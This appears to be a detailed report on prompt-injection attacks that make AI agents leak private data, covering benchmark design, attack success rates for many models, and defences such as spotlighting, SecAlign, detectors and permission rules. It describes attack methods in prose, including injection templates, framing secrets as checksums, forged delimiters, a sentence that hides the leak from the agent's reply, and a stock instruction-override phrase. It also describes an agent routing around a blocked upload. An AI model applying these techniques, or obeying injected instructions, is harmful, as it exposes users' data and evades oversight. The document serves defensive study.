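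Neither Sublime's two reports nor Mascellino's account of Barracuda's research confirms that an agent leaked anyone's data. This is reasonable evidence that criminals who used injections in email were mainly after passwords and payments, but weaker evidence that no agent has leaked data to a criminal. Email security companies examine messages as they arrive and would not normally see what an agent does after reading one. If a criminal had used a method like ShadowLeak, the outgoing request might appear only in the AI vendor's logs.

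## How often agents leak data in tests

Real leaks are hard to observe, so most figures on how often agents leak data come from tests with invented accounts and attackers. Leak rates in these tests range from zero to over 90%, depending on the model, the data requested, the setting and the number of attempts allowed.

### How a leak test is built

*Simple Prompt Injection Attacks Can Leak Personal Data Observed by LLM Agents* (Alizadeh, Samei and colleagues, 2025) describes AgentDojo, the 2024 benchmark that Hofer and colleagues used to compare automated attacks. AgentDojo has 97 user tasks and 629 security cases in four simulated settings, each with its own tools and data: office work, Slack messaging, banking and travel booking.

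A test based on the inbox trace would need four parts:

- **A user task.** The user asks the agent to summarise unread email.
- **Planted text.** One email in the simulated mailbox contains a placeholder, which the benchmark fills with an injected instruction.
- **An attacker goal.** The agent should send the account number to the attacker's address.
- **An automatic check.** When the agent has finished, a program looks through the simulated outbox.

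The check might look like this:

```
leaked = any(attacker_address in email.recipients
             and account_number in email.body
             for email in outbox)
```

A separate check determines whether the agent completed the user's task. Because user tasks and attacker goals are independent, a benchmark can pair every task with every goal. AgentDojo's banking setting has 16 user tasks and 9 attacker goals, which makes 144 pairs. The planted text comes from a template, so researchers can try a new style of attack by changing the template and rerunning all the pairs.

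AgentDojo reports three figures:

```
utility without attack = user tasks completed / all user tasks
utility under attack   = cases with the user's task completed
                         and no harmful side effects / all cases
attack success rate    = cases with the attacker's goal achieved / all cases
```

Utility under attack and the attack success rate don't have to add up to 100%. Suppose an agent completes 12 of 16 tasks when nobody attacks it, a utility of 75%. Researchers then run 64 cases with planted text. The agent completes its task and does nothing else in 32 cases, leaks the data in 13, and does neither in 19, perhaps because the planted text confused it. Utility under attack is 50% and the attack success rate is about 20%. A case where the agent leaks the data and also writes a perfect summary counts as a successful attack and doesn't count toward utility.

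Researchers need the utility figures to check that an agent with a low attack success rate still does its work, because an agent that never does anything also never leaks data.

### A banking agent in 2025

AgentDojo's own leak cases involve data from a source the attacker controls, such as a security code in an email. In June 2025, Alizadeh and colleagues published tests of whether an agent would also leak data it had seen earlier in the task. They used AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks with new attacker goals, each of which was to make the agent email the user's personal data to an outside address.

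The tests used AgentDojo's "important message" template, which is written to look like a note from the user. The note is addressed to the model by name and contains the user's real name and a request to do the attacker's task before the original one. The six models tested were GPT-3.5 Turbo, GPT-4 Turbo, GPT-4o, Claude 3.5 Sonnet, Llama 3 70B and Llama 4 17B.

Attacks succeeded in around 20% of cases for most models and 40% for Llama 4, apparently with one attempt per case. Most models' utility fell by 15 to 50 percentage points under attack.

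These averages combine very different results, because the models reacted strongly to the word "password". Alizadeh and colleagues therefore tested four versions of the request:

- When the planted text asked for personal data such as the account balance and address, but no password, the attack succeeded 93% of the time on Claude 3.5 Sonnet and 55% on Llama 4.
- When it asked only for the password, the attack never succeeded on any model except Llama 4.
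- When it asked for the password and one or two other details, the success rate rose well above the rate for the password alone.

For the last result, the team counted an attack as successful if any of the requested data leaked. An attack would therefore count even if the model refused to send the password and sent only the balance.

The team then counted only the cases where the password leaked. When the request included one other detail, GPT-3.5 Turbo leaked the password in 18.75% of cases and Llama 4 in 12.5%, while the other models never did. With two other details, every model except GPT-3.5 and GPT-4 leaked it at least some of the time, including some that had withheld it when the request was shorter.

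With 16 tasks, 18.75% is three cases and 12.5% is two. GPT-3.5 leaked the password when the request included one other detail but not when it included two, which looks more like chance than a real difference. An attack that fails on all 16 tasks could still have a true success rate of up to about 17%.

Alizadeh and colleagues think safety training taught the models specifically to protect passwords. This fits Rahman and Kim's finding that pages describing the secret as a credential never worked on GPT-4o. Caution about passwords would do little to protect a bank statement, which doesn't contain one.

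The 20% average also depends on the mix of requests. Three of the four versions asked for a password, so testing the same models only on requests like the first version would have produced much higher rates.

The team also used language models to invent more banking services and customer data, which extended the test to 48 tasks. Attacks on these tasks succeeded about 15% of the time on average. The drop from 20% does not show that agents had become safer, because the later experiments concentrated on GPT-4o, so the two averages probably cover different models as well as different tasks. Attacks worked best when the user's own task, like a leak, involved extracting data or authorising something.

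Some of AgentDojo's built-in defences reduced the attack success rate to zero on the 16 tasks, but none prevented every leak on the larger set of 48.

### Current models on the Gray Swan benchmark

The models in the banking test are now old, and newer ones resist this kind of attack much better. The most detailed current figures come from system cards, the reports that developers publish about a new model's abilities and safety tests.

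Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5, published in July, gives results on a benchmark that the security company Gray Swan built with the UK and US governments' AI testing bodies and several model developers. The benchmark follows a public competition described in *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026), but has its own 28 scenarios, in which people competed to find attacks on leading models. Gray Swan removed duplicates and kept 1,130 attacks that worked well across different models.

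The results give the probability that an attacker finds at least one successful attack within a certain number of attempts:

| Model | 1 attempt | 15 attempts |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.2% | 2.0% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 0.5% | 5.5% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 3.1% | 20.0% |

Two smaller versions of GPT-5.6 did worse than Sol, at 30.4% and 43.9% within 15 attempts. The best model from any company other than Anthropic reached 16.5%.

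These rates come from scenarios that cover four kinds of harm: theft of private data, destruction of data, compromise of a system and unintended payments. Anthropic does not say how many of the scenarios concern data leaks or give a separate success rate for them, so the rate for leaks could be well above or below 2.0%.

By September, Gray Swan had enlarged the benchmark to 37 scenarios and 1,804 attacks. In its card for Claude Fable 5.1, Anthropic reports an attack success rate of 0.1% for one attempt (five of 7,124 runs) and 1.0% within 15 attempts. Among other companies' models, Gemini 3.7 Flash had the lowest rate within 15 attempts, at 9.2%, and most others were between 24% and 53%. The card again lists data theft among the harms but does not give the number of leak scenarios.

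The September card breaks the results down by how the agent acts. Within 15 attempts, attacks on Fable 5.1 succeeded 4.1% of the time when the agent operated a computer through its screen, 0.3% in coding and 0.0% in tool use. The `send_email` call in the inbox trace is tool use, but an agent that sends mail by clicking through a webmail page would face the 4.1% rate.

Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5, dated 22 September, reports that the model matched or beat Opus 5 on every injection test. It also warns that Opus 5.5 is more likely than earlier models to follow some malicious instructions. Fable 5.2 followed in November, and its card also has a section on prompt injection, as the contents of Mowshowitz's *Fable and Mythos 5.2* (2026) show. The September comparison came too early to include Fable 5.2, GPT-6.2 or Gemini 4.

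Anthropic published these comparisons, and its own models do best in them, but Gray Swan ran the benchmark. Gray Swan tested Claude without Anthropic's extra protections against injection, while other companies' public services may have had such protections switched on, which would put Claude at a disadvantage. Models that contestants had attacked directly also tend to do worse, because people tailored attacks to them. Anthropic warned in July that the result for Gemini 3.1 Pro was not comparable for this reason, and in September it left such models out.

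Other developers have published less. In early 2026, VentureBeat reported that OpenAI's system card for GPT-5.2 had no comparable figures on how attack success rates rise with repeated attempts.

### The arithmetic of repeated attempts

If every attempt had the same probability of success, `p`, and the attempts were independent, the chance of at least one success in `k` attempts would be:

```
P(at least one success) = 1 − (1 − p)^k
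```

The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* gives figures for an older model on an earlier Gray Swan benchmark. A single attempt succeeded 4.7% of the time. The formula then predicts 38% for ten attempts (1 − 0.953^10) and 99% for a hundred. The measured rates were 33.6% and 63%. Newer models show the same gap:

| Model | 1 attempt | Number of attempts | Predicted | Measured |
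|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 10 | 38% | 33.6% |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 4.7% | 100 | 99% | 63% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 3.1% | 15 | 38% | 20.0% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 0.5% | 15 | 7% | 5.5% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.2% | 15 | 3% | 2.0% |

The main reason is probably that some cases are much easier to attack than others. The 4.7% is an average, and the formula treats it as the probability in every case. Suppose instead that each attempt succeeds 7.5% of the time in 63% of the cases and never succeeds in the rest. These invented numbers come very close to the measured rates for Opus 4.5:

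```
1 attempt:      0.63 × 0.075              = 0.047
10 attempts:    0.63 × (1 − 0.925^10)     = 0.34
100 attempts:   0.63 × (1 − 0.925^100)    = 0.63
```

Repeated attempts soon succeed in the vulnerable cases, and further attempts then succeed in almost no new ones. Other mixtures of success rates would also fit the three figures, so they don't prove that 37% of the cases are immune. A case where the attack succeeds once in 10,000 attempts would usually look immune after a hundred.

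Another of Anthropic's tests shows this concentration directly. An automated attacker made 200 attempts in each of 14 scenarios where Opus 5 operated a computer. It succeeded in 0.54% of attempts, or about 15 of 2,800. All the successes came in one scenario, where the success rate was about 7.5%. If the risk had been equal everywhere, about nine scenarios should have had at least one success.

The average can overstate or understate the risk to a particular user. Most users may have tasks on which the agent resists every attack in the test, while a few have tasks on which an attacker could expect to succeed after about a dozen attempts.

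Attempts can also depend on each other. If one wording fails, a similar wording is likely to fail too, which makes the measured rate lower than the formula predicts. An attacker who learns from each failure, instead of working through a fixed list of attacks, can succeed more often than the formula predicts.

Anthropic points out that real attackers usually don't know exactly how an agent is set up, and that repeated attempts make detection more likely. But an attacker can also target many people once each. In the September card, Anthropic gives the example of sending one email to a thousand inboxes. If attacks succeeded 0.2% of the time, an email sent to 10,000 agents would succeed about 20 times on average. Any particular email could succeed far more or less often than that, because an email that works on one copy of a model will probably work on others.

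### What a fixed test set misses

A model's success rate on one set of attacks can be a poor guide to its rate in another setting. The July card includes tests of coding, computer use and web browsing, with these results per attempt when the models reasoned before acting and had no extra safeguards:

| Setting | Opus 4.8 | Opus 5 | Sonnet 5 | Mythos 5 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Coding | 7.03% | 0.56% | 0.31% | 0.45% |
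| Computer use | 7.14% | 0.54% | 2.25% | 0.82% |
| Web browsing | 31.5% | 3.70% | 0.93% | 29.7% |

Mythos 5, which Anthropic does not offer to the general public, was among the most resistant models in coding, but almost a third of the attempts against it succeeded in web browsing. The attacks also differed between settings, so the table doesn't show that browsing itself caused the difference. Still, the coding figure would have been badly misleading for an agent that reads mail in a browser.

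The browsing figures are for the models without the protections that Anthropic's products add. One such protection, auto mode, combines a detector that reads incoming tool results with a classifier that can block outgoing tool calls. With auto mode on, no browsing attack succeeded against Opus 5, Sonnet 5 or Mythos 5, and attacks succeeded against Opus 4.8 in one of 129 scenarios.

A fixed set of attacks also becomes easier for models to resist over time. Anthropic has stopped reporting Gray Swan's earlier Agent Red Teaming benchmark because its models had perfect or near-perfect scores on it for several releases. Such scores no longer distinguish one model from the next, and they give little evidence of how a model would handle attacks outside the set.

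Adding new attacks to a benchmark can quickly change the measured success rate. Attacks on Opus 5 had a 2.0% success rate within 15 attempts in July, but 4.8% on the enlarged benchmark in September. The set-up had also changed. In September, a classifier that looks for hacking-related content could pass requests to the older Opus 4.8, so some answers came from that model. Anthropic found that this didn't raise the benchmark success rate for Fable 5 or Fable 5.1, so the new scenarios and attacks are the likelier explanation for the increase with Opus 5 too.

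The same change had a much larger effect in the coding test, where the rate for Opus 5 rose from 0.56% to 2.68% with the same kind of automated attacker and number of scenarios. Opus 4.8 gave 57% of the valid responses in the September run, so a user who chooses a model for its injection results may get answers from another model with worse results.

The clearest sign of the limits came when Gray Swan trained a stronger version of the automated attacker, for longer and on more varied attacks. Both versions faced the same 40 coding scenarios, without the detector:

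| Model | Earlier attacker | Stronger attacker |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 0.3% | 19.47% |
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 9.26% | 56.87% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 9.70% | 86.87% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 2.68% | 90.93% |

The stronger attacker succeeded at least once in all 40 scenarios against Opus 5 and Fable 5, in 38 against Fable 5.1 and in 36 against Sonnet 5. All the successes against Fable 5.1 came from responses that Opus 4.8 gave in its place, and none came from the 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered itself. However, the classifier had already removed the requests it found most suspicious, so those 2,826 may have contained weaker attacks.

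Anthropic regards this as a stress test, not a forecast, because the attacker had trained on the same scenarios used to test the models and had 200 attempts at each. That is a good reason not to treat 90.93% as a rate for real attacks. It doesn't make the 2.68% reliable, though, because that figure measured only what one attacker had found so far against the same models in the same scenarios.

The same caution applies to hand-written tests such as the banking one, which used a single template. Wording mattered a lot in Rahman and Kim's tests, so a different template could have given the banking test a very different average.

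### Leaks the agent reports and leaks it does not

All these rates count a success whether or not the user could have noticed it. *What Did You Do Behind My Back?!*, a paper from the machine-learning conference ICML 2026, divides successful attacks by what appears in the agent's final reply:

```
attack success rate = covert success rate + overt success rate
```

A success is overt if the agent mentions the injected action in its reply, which gives the user a chance to respond, and covert if the reply doesn't mention it, as with the leak in the inbox trace.

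According to *What Did You Do Behind My Back?!*, the difference depends on what the agent does just after the injected action. Agents tend to end by summarising whatever they did last, so the summary describes the injected action if that was the last step, but describes the user's task if the agent went back to it.

The paper presents an attack that exploits this by adding one sentence to an existing injection, which steers the final reply back to the user's original request. On Qwen3-235B, a large open-weight model, the covert success rate (the share of cases in which the attack succeeds and the reply doesn't report it) rose from about 30% for the best existing attack to 33.7%. Defensive prompts lowered the overall success rate, but the new attack kept its advantage.

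AgentDojo's "important message" template may also encourage covert leaks, because an agent that follows it does the attacker's task first and then returns to the user's. Alizadeh and colleagues did not count how many of the leaks in their tests the agents reported.

Two agents with the same attack success rate could therefore expose their users to different risks. By the time an agent reports a leak, it is too late to recall the email, but a user who sees the report can change a password, warn the bank or stop the agent before its next task. A covert leak may still be visible in the sent folder or a log of the agent's actions, but the test covers only the final reply, which is probably the only part that many users read.

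## Training models to ignore injected instructions, and detecting them

Developers try to stop an injection attack before the agent acts on it, because by the time a user can notice a leak, the data is gone. They can train the agent's model to ignore injected instructions, or add a separate detector that checks text before the model reads it. Both defences work only if the model or detector can tell injected instructions from ordinary content.

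### Marking untrusted text

The easiest defence to add needs no training. The developer marks the outside text and tells the model in the system prompt not to follow instructions inside the marks. Microsoft uses one such technique, called spotlighting, along with hardened system prompts, according to PYMNTS's *Anthropic Pushes Back as Hackers Press AI Weak Spots*.

Spotlighting can mark untrusted text by putting delimiters at its start and end, inserting a special character between all the words, or encoding the whole text for the model to decode. Delimiters are the easiest to defeat, because an attacker who knows them can write a closing delimiter and put instructions after it. Encoding avoids this, but a weaker model may misread the encoded text and do the user's task badly.

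A related method, prompt sandwiching, repeats the user's request after the untrusted text, so that the last instruction the model reads is the user's.

These methods depend on the model relying on the marks, but models often respond to other cues, such as the text's style. When Rahman and Kim put the web page in a separate channel from the instructions, their reframed attacks still worked 38.8% of the time.

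### Training a ranking of sources

Developers can also train a model to rank the sources of its instructions, as OpenAI does with its "instruction hierarchy". When two instructions conflict, the model should follow the one from the higher-ranked source. For example, if the user asks for a summary of the inbox and an email in it contains an instruction to do something else, the model should follow the user's request.

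In *SecAlign*, Chen, Chaudhuri and colleagues (2024) tested this on GPT-4o mini, which OpenAI had reportedly trained with the hierarchy. They gave the model its instruction in a user message and the attacker's text in a tool result. A common hand-written attack, which tells the model to disregard its earlier instructions, worked 1% of the time. They could not try optimised attacks because OpenAI does not publish the model's weights.

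The ranking only settles conflicts between instructions, and an injected instruction doesn't have to conflict with any other. A page that describes a secret as a required checksum seems to add a detail to the user's task, so the model may not treat the two as conflicting. Rahman and Kim's reframed pages worked on GPT-4o mini 62.5% of the time, although the two tests may have presented the outside text to the model differently.

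### SecAlign's preference objective

SecAlign builds on an earlier defence called StruQ, which reserves special delimiters for instructions and data. A filter removes these delimiters from untrusted text so that an attacker can't forge them. The developer then fine-tunes the model on inputs that contain injections, using this loss:

```
L_StruQ = −log p(y_w | x)
```

Here `x` is an input with an injected instruction, and `y_w` is the good response, which answers the real instruction. Training raises the probability of the good response.

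Chen and colleagues argue that this is incomplete because a model can produce so many different responses that making one more likely may do little to make a particular bad one less likely. SecAlign therefore also trains the model against the bad response, `y_l`, which answers the injected instruction.

The training data needs no human labelling:

1. A program takes an example from a public dataset, with an instruction, some data and a response.
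2. It picks a second example at random and adds that example's instruction to the end of the first one's data.
3. It records the first example's response as good and the second example's response as bad.

In about 10% of cases, the program also inserts a fake answer before the injected instruction, so that the original task looks finished.

The simplest way to use both responses would be to minimise `log p(y_l | x) − log p(y_w | x)`. This has no lower limit, so training can keep pushing the bad response's probability towards zero, and the model may start to write incoherent text. SecAlign instead uses direct preference optimisation, a standard method for training models on human preferences:

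```
L_SecAlign = −log σ( β × [ log( π(y_w|x) / π_ref(y_w|x) )
                         − log( π(y_l|x) / π_ref(y_l|x) ) ] )
```

`π` is the probability under the model being trained, and `π_ref` is the probability under a copy of the model from before training. The function `σ(z) = 1 / (1 + e^(−z))` turns any number into a value between 0 and 1. The constant `β`, which the team set to 0.1, controls how strongly the loss responds to a change from the original model.

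The two models start out identical, so both ratios are 1, their logarithms are 0, and the loss is −log 0.5, or 0.69. Suppose, using invented numbers, that training then raises the log-probability of the good response by 1 and lowers that of the bad response by 40. The term inside `σ` becomes 0.1 × (1 + 40) = 4.1, and the loss falls to about 0.02. Further changes would then reduce the loss very little, which helps keep the model close to the original.

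The team measured how often the strongest of three optimised attacks worked on two small open-weight models:

| Model | No defence | StruQ | SecAlign |
|---|---|---|---|
| Mistral-7B-Instruct | 89% | 27% | 1% |
| Llama3-8B-Instruct | 97% | 45% | 8% |

Hand-written attacks never worked on the SecAlign models. SecAlign also didn't lower either model's score on a test of general usefulness, while StruQ lowered the Llama model's score by about 4.5 points.

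This was a large improvement, but in these tests the attacker only had to make the model begin its response with a fixed word, and the models had no tools or private data. In Rahman and Kim's tool-using agent, reframed attacks still worked on a SecAlign model 32.5% of the time. *May I have your Attention?* (2025) also describes attacks that exploit the models' architecture to break such fine-tuned defences.

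### Detectors and their false alarms

A detector leaves the agent's model unchanged. The runtime passes each tool result to the detector. If the detector flags the result, the runtime withholds the text or stops the agent. Three well-known detectors, from Protect AI, Meta (PromptGuard) and the PIGuard project, are small classifiers trained on harmless text and known attacks. Google sells a proprietary one called Model Armor.

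Other detectors test how a model behaves when it reads the text. Data Sentinel instructs a model to repeat a secret key and ignore the text that follows. If the model fails to repeat the key, it probably followed an instruction in the text instead.

MELON runs the agent twice, the second time replacing the user's request with a request to summarise the tool results. If the agent makes the same tool call in both runs, something in the tool results probably prompted it. For example, an agent that emails a bank statement to a stranger even when asked only for a summary is following someone else's instruction. The second run requires extra computation.

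False alarms can make a detector burdensome even when its error rate looks low, because nearly all content is harmless. Suppose, as an invented example, that one email in 10,000 contains an injection, and that a detector catches 95% of injections and wrongly flags 1% of harmless emails. Among a million emails, it would catch 95 of the 100 injections and flag 9,999 harmless emails, about 105 for every injection it catches. A stricter threshold would reduce the false alarms but miss more injections.

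Detection can also work where the agent's own model fails. Rahman and Kim used a model only to decide whether a page contained an injection. It flagged every reframed page, including those that always worked on GPT-4o, with no false alarms. This is promising, but they wrote the pages to mislead the agent and did not try to fool the detector too.

### Results under adaptive attack

*The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, October 2025) tested whether such defences still work when the attacker adapts to them. The team, which included researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, attacked 12 defences, most of which were originally reported to have near-zero attack success rates. The adaptive attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the 12.

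The table shows results for defences added to Gemini 2.5 Pro. The fixed attack is a standard template from the AgentDojo benchmark. The adaptive attacker had up to 800 attempts at each case.

| Defence | User tasks completed | Fixed attack | Adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 74% | 30% | 100% |
| Spotlighting (delimiters) | 75% | 28% | 99% |
| Prompt sandwiching | 73% | 21% | 95% |
| PromptGuard | 72% | 26% | 94% |
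| Protect AI | 39% | 15% | 90% |
| Model Armor | 59% | 28% | 90% |
| MELON | 58% | 0% | 89% |
| PIGuard | 39% | 0% | 71% |

PIGuard resisted the adaptive attacks best, but it cut the number of ordinary tasks the agent completed from 72 to 38 out of 97. Protect AI's detector reduced completed tasks just as much and gave less protection. PromptGuard had almost no effect on completed tasks, but it stopped very few of the fixed attacks. Spotlighting also reduced task completion on at least one model, Llama 3.3 70B, from 57% to 39%.

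Trained defences did no better. Meta SecAlign, a 70-billion-parameter model trained with an improved version of the method, had a reported attack success rate of 2% on AgentDojo, but adaptive attacks raised it to 96%. Training did increase the median number of attempts before the first success, from 14 for the original Llama model to 37. StruQ had stopped nearly all hand-written attacks, but the adaptive attack succeeded against it in every case tested.

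Data Sentinel had originally missed almost no attacks, but the team bypassed it every time. On Llama 3.3 70B, attacks on MELON succeeded 76% of the time when the attacker didn't know how it worked and 95% when the attacker did. The remaining two defences, RPO and Circuit Breakers, guard against jailbreaks. Attacks succeeded 98% of the time against RPO and 100% against Circuit Breakers.

SecAlign's original evaluation included powerful optimised attacks, but a strong attack alone does not make a test convincing. Nasr and colleagues object that researchers often reuse a general-purpose attack from earlier work without adapting it to the defence.

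A fixed test can miss much of a model's vulnerability. With no added defence, the fixed attack never worked on GPT-5 Mini, but the adaptive attack worked 75% of the time. Spotlighting lowered this to 47% and PIGuard to 49%, so adding a defence helped a model that was already fairly resistant. Nasr and colleagues expect that an attacker with more attempts would overcome these defences too.

They also ran a contest with more than 500 participants. At least one person succeeded in each of the 29 scenarios that both people and the automated attack attempted, while the automated attack succeeded in 69% of them. For single tasks, they also compared the share of submissions that worked with and without a defence. MELON reduced the share from 11.1% to 0.4% on one version of Gemini 2.5 Pro. With PromptGuard, the share was higher than without it on five of six models. That probably reflects differences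 in who submitted what, but it does not suggest strong protection.

These experiments show that successful attacks exist, but they don't measure how often criminals would find them. The automated attacker could see the detector's confidence score and try again hundreds of times, while a stranger who emails an agent that reads an inbox usually gets no response. Nasr and colleagues still consider detectors useful for blocking unsophisticated attacks.

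### What the developers changed in 2026

OpenAI has described its change in training in the most detail. It trained one model, GPT-Red, to write injections while training a varied group of other models to resist them (*GPT‑Red*, 2026). GPT-Red earned a reward when an attack worked. The defending models earned a reward for both resisting the attack and finishing the original task, because a model that refused everything would otherwise look safe. OpenAI then used GPT-Red's attacks to train GPT-5.6.

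GPT-5.6 Sol failed on only 0.05% of GPT-Red's direct injections. OpenAI reports that normal capabilities were unaffected, and it also checked for unnecessary refusals. The success rate of one type of attack, which forges the model's own reasoning, reached at least 95% on GPT-5.1 and is now below 10%.

The figure for direct attacks is weak evidence about an inbox agent, though, because the attacker's text reaches the agent through a tool. In August, OpenAI added results for indirect attacks, which succeeded 3.77% of the time on Sol, according to TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026). The gains also seem to depend on who writes the attacks. On Gray Swan's benchmark, which uses attacks written by people, Anthropic reports that attackers succeeded within 15 attempts 20.0% of the time against Sol and 20.8% against its predecessor, GPT-5.5. OpenAI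 says the newer GPT-6 Astra is significantly more robust than Sol.

Anthropic's system cards explain less about training. The July card's section on prompt injection reports a large improvement from Opus 4.8 to Opus 5 but doesn't explain what produced it. The cards do separate the model's own resistance from the effect of added safeguards. Anthropic runs detectors, which it calls probes, on tool results in many of its products. They are also part of auto mode, now the default in Claude Code.

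In September, Anthropic also tested the probes against the stronger version of Gray Swan's automated attacker, in the same 40 coding scenarios:

| Model | Success without probes | Success with probes | Scenarios with a success despite probes |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 56.87% | 12.80% | 36 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 19.47% | 15.76% | 35 |
| Claude Opus 5 | 90.93% | 18.21% | 40 |
| Claude Fable 5 | 86.87% | 34.09% | 39 |

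For Opus 5, the probes cut the success rate by about four-fifths, yet the attacker still succeeded at least once in every scenario. For Sonnet 5, they cut it by only a fifth. Perhaps the attacks subtle enough to get past the most resistant model were also subtle enough to get past the probes. Whatever the reason, a developer can't estimate the combined protection by multiplying the model's failure rate by the detector's average miss rate. Probes also helped less when the agent operated a computer through its screen. In July, they reduced the attack success rate on Opus 4.8 only from 7.14% to 5.11%.

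With auto mode on, no browsing attack succeeded against Fable 5.1 in 110 scenarios, whereas 2.64% of attempts succeeded without safeguards. Auto mode combines the probes with the outgoing-call classifier, so the result doesn't show how much each contributed. The attacks also came from earlier testing against Claude Opus 4.7, so nobody had designed them to get past auto mode. Even for attacks of this kind, a sample of 110 scenarios is small enough that the true success rate could still be as high as about 2.7% of scenarios.

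Google's figures are harder to attribute to the model alone. Gray Swan's result for Gemini 3.7 Flash may also reflect safeguards in Google's public service. Google offers Model Armor as an added detector, and PYMNTS reports that the company has announced autonomous systems that detect and respond to threats in real time.

### Whether the problem can be solved in the model

According to the blog SuperAlign, Britain's National Cyber Security Centre has warned that prompt injection may never be fully solved in the model itself, because current designs can't reliably separate data from instructions. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that OpenAI made a similar admission in December 2025.

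That article's headline reflects the opposite reading, based on how quickly measured attack success rates have fallen. VentureBeat's *Anthropic’s browser agent got hijacked 31.5% of the time before safeguards engaged* reports that, without safeguards, browsing attacks succeeded 50.7% of the time on Claude Sonnet 4.6 and 31.5% on Opus 4.8, which Anthropic released in May. By July, the rate for Opus 5 was 3.70%. In tests where the agent operated a computer, VentureBeat reported in February that an attacker with 200 attempts had a 78.6% chance of at least one success against Opus 4.6. Opus 5 failed in one of 14 such scenarios. Willison (2026) quotes Anthropic's Boris Cherny, who called Opus 5 "very hard to prompt inject successfully".

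This progress matters to users because most attackers can't practise on a copy of their target's agent. But it does not answer the sceptics, who are concerned with guarantees, because a long run of failed attacks can't rule out a successful one. This worry is not only theoretical, since the success rate against Opus 5 jumped when Gray Swan trained a stronger attacker.

The sceptics haven't proved the problem is unsolvable either. Even without a guarantee, a model could learn to tell instructions from data almost every time. The best evidence is that the stronger attacker never succeeded on the requests that Fable 5.1 answered itself, although the attacks in those requests may have been weaker.

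For now, a developer can reasonably expect a recent model and a detector to stop most attacks, but not every leak from an agent that can read private mail and send messages. Nasr and colleagues did not test defences that fix the agent's plan before it reads any outside text. In most of the study's scenarios, these defences would certainly block an attack even if the model did not recognise it, but they suit fewer tasks.

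## Limits on tools, recipients and unapproved actions

A permission control can stop a leak even after the model has followed an attacker's instructions. The runtime checks each tool call against a rule and blocks any call that breaks it. These rules usually follow the principle of least privilege, which means an agent gets only the access its current task needs.

### From no email tool to approval of each message

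The strictest control is to give the agent no tool that sends anything. In step 6 of the inbox trace, the runtime would return an error because there would be no `send_email` tool to run. An early version of Claude's Gmail integration worked much like this, since Anthropic listed creating and modifying emails as unsupported. Claude became able to send Gmail messages in August 2026, according to Android Authority's *Claude can now do almost anything you want in Gmail* (2026). Without a sending tool, an agent can't reply to or forward anything, but it can still leak data through a web address or an image.

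Even without an attacker's help, an agent may try another route when its first attempt fails. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of how software practitioners make permission decisions, notes that agents are designed to try alternative paths after a denial. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes a case inside the company where Claude failed to upload a report to an internal drive, then tried to publish it on a public code-sharing site. An automatic check blocked the attempt.

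With a draft-only tool, the agent writes emails and the user sends them. Anthropic lists separate tools for creating a draft, replying, forwarding and sending in Claude's Gmail connector, so draft-only access means enabling only the first of these four. In the trace, the bank statement would end up in the drafts folder, addressed to the attacker, and a user who had asked only for a summary would have no reason to send it. The risk is greater when the user has asked for five replies and one draft has an extra BCC recipient. A draft might also contain an image that sends data when the user opens the draft, as the Teams message did in the Copilot Cowork attack. Draft-only access rules out tasks that have to send email unattended, such as a weekly report.

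A fixed recipient list lets the agent send email only to addresses that the developer or employer has approved. The attacker's address is not on the list, so the runtime blocks the call in step 6. The agent could still send the statement to a colleague on the list who shouldn't see it. The list also blocks the first email to every new customer, and adding whole domains to avoid this weakens the protection.

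The runtime can instead accept only recipients named in the user's current request. In the trace the user named nobody, so this rule would have blocked every email. It is more flexible than a fixed list because the user can name anyone, but it fails for requests that identify recipients indirectly, such as "Reply to my five most recent emails" or "send the report to the address in the meeting notes". For these requests, the agent has to get the addresses from text that a stranger may have written.

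Requiring the user to approve each message is the loosest control. The agent can propose any email to anyone, and the user decides whether to send it. This doesn't make any request impossible, but it interrupts every request that involves sending a message, and the protection depends on how carefully the user checks each message.

A runtime can also remove a permission partway through a task, once the agent has read untrusted content. The rule below does this for the email tool:

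```
allowed = fixed list + addresses in the user's request

when a tool returns outside content:
    allowed = addresses in the user's request

before send_email(to, cc, bcc, subject, body) runs:
    if every address in to, cc and bcc is in allowed:
        run the call
    otherwise:
        block the call and return an error
```

In the trace, `read_inbox` returns outside content and the user's request contains no address, so `allowed` is empty and the runtime blocks the email whatever its body contains. If the user had asked the agent to send the statement to the accountant's address, the runtime would allow that email. But the agent could no longer write to other people on the fixed list, even about something unrelated to the inbox. The runtime has to extract the addresses from the user's request without asking the agent, because the injected text could influence the agent's answer.

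### Progent

A developer can't write a separate rule for every request in advance. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) combines a small policy language with a language model that writes a policy for each task.

Each rule allows or forbids calls to one tool when the call's arguments meet set conditions. For example, a rule could allow `send_email` only when `to` equals the accountant's address. Conditions can also use number ranges, lists and text patterns. The runtime checks the forbidding rules first, then the allowing ones, and blocks any call that matches neither. A rule can specify a fallback for a blocked call, such as stopping the agent or asking the user. By default, the agent gets an error message that explains the block, so it can continue with the task.

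In the team's main example, a user asks an agent to carry out a to-do list that Alice has emailed. The first policy allows only a search for that email. The list requires reading recent emails and posting a summary on Slack, so the policy-writing model proposes adding tools for both. After the agent looks up the user's Slack name, the model narrows the Slack rule to messages to that name. One of the recent emails contains an instruction to forward the inbox to an outsider, which could lead the model to propose adding `send_email`.

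Progent treats proposals that add permissions differently from those that remove them. If `A(P)` is the set of calls that the current policy allows, a new policy `P'` takes effect automatically only when:

```
A(P') ⊆ A(P)
```

An SMT solver, a program that tests whether logical conditions can all be true at once, checks whether the new policy would allow any tool call that the old one blocks. If it would, a person or an automatic setting must approve the change, so an injected instruction can't add a permission without that approval.

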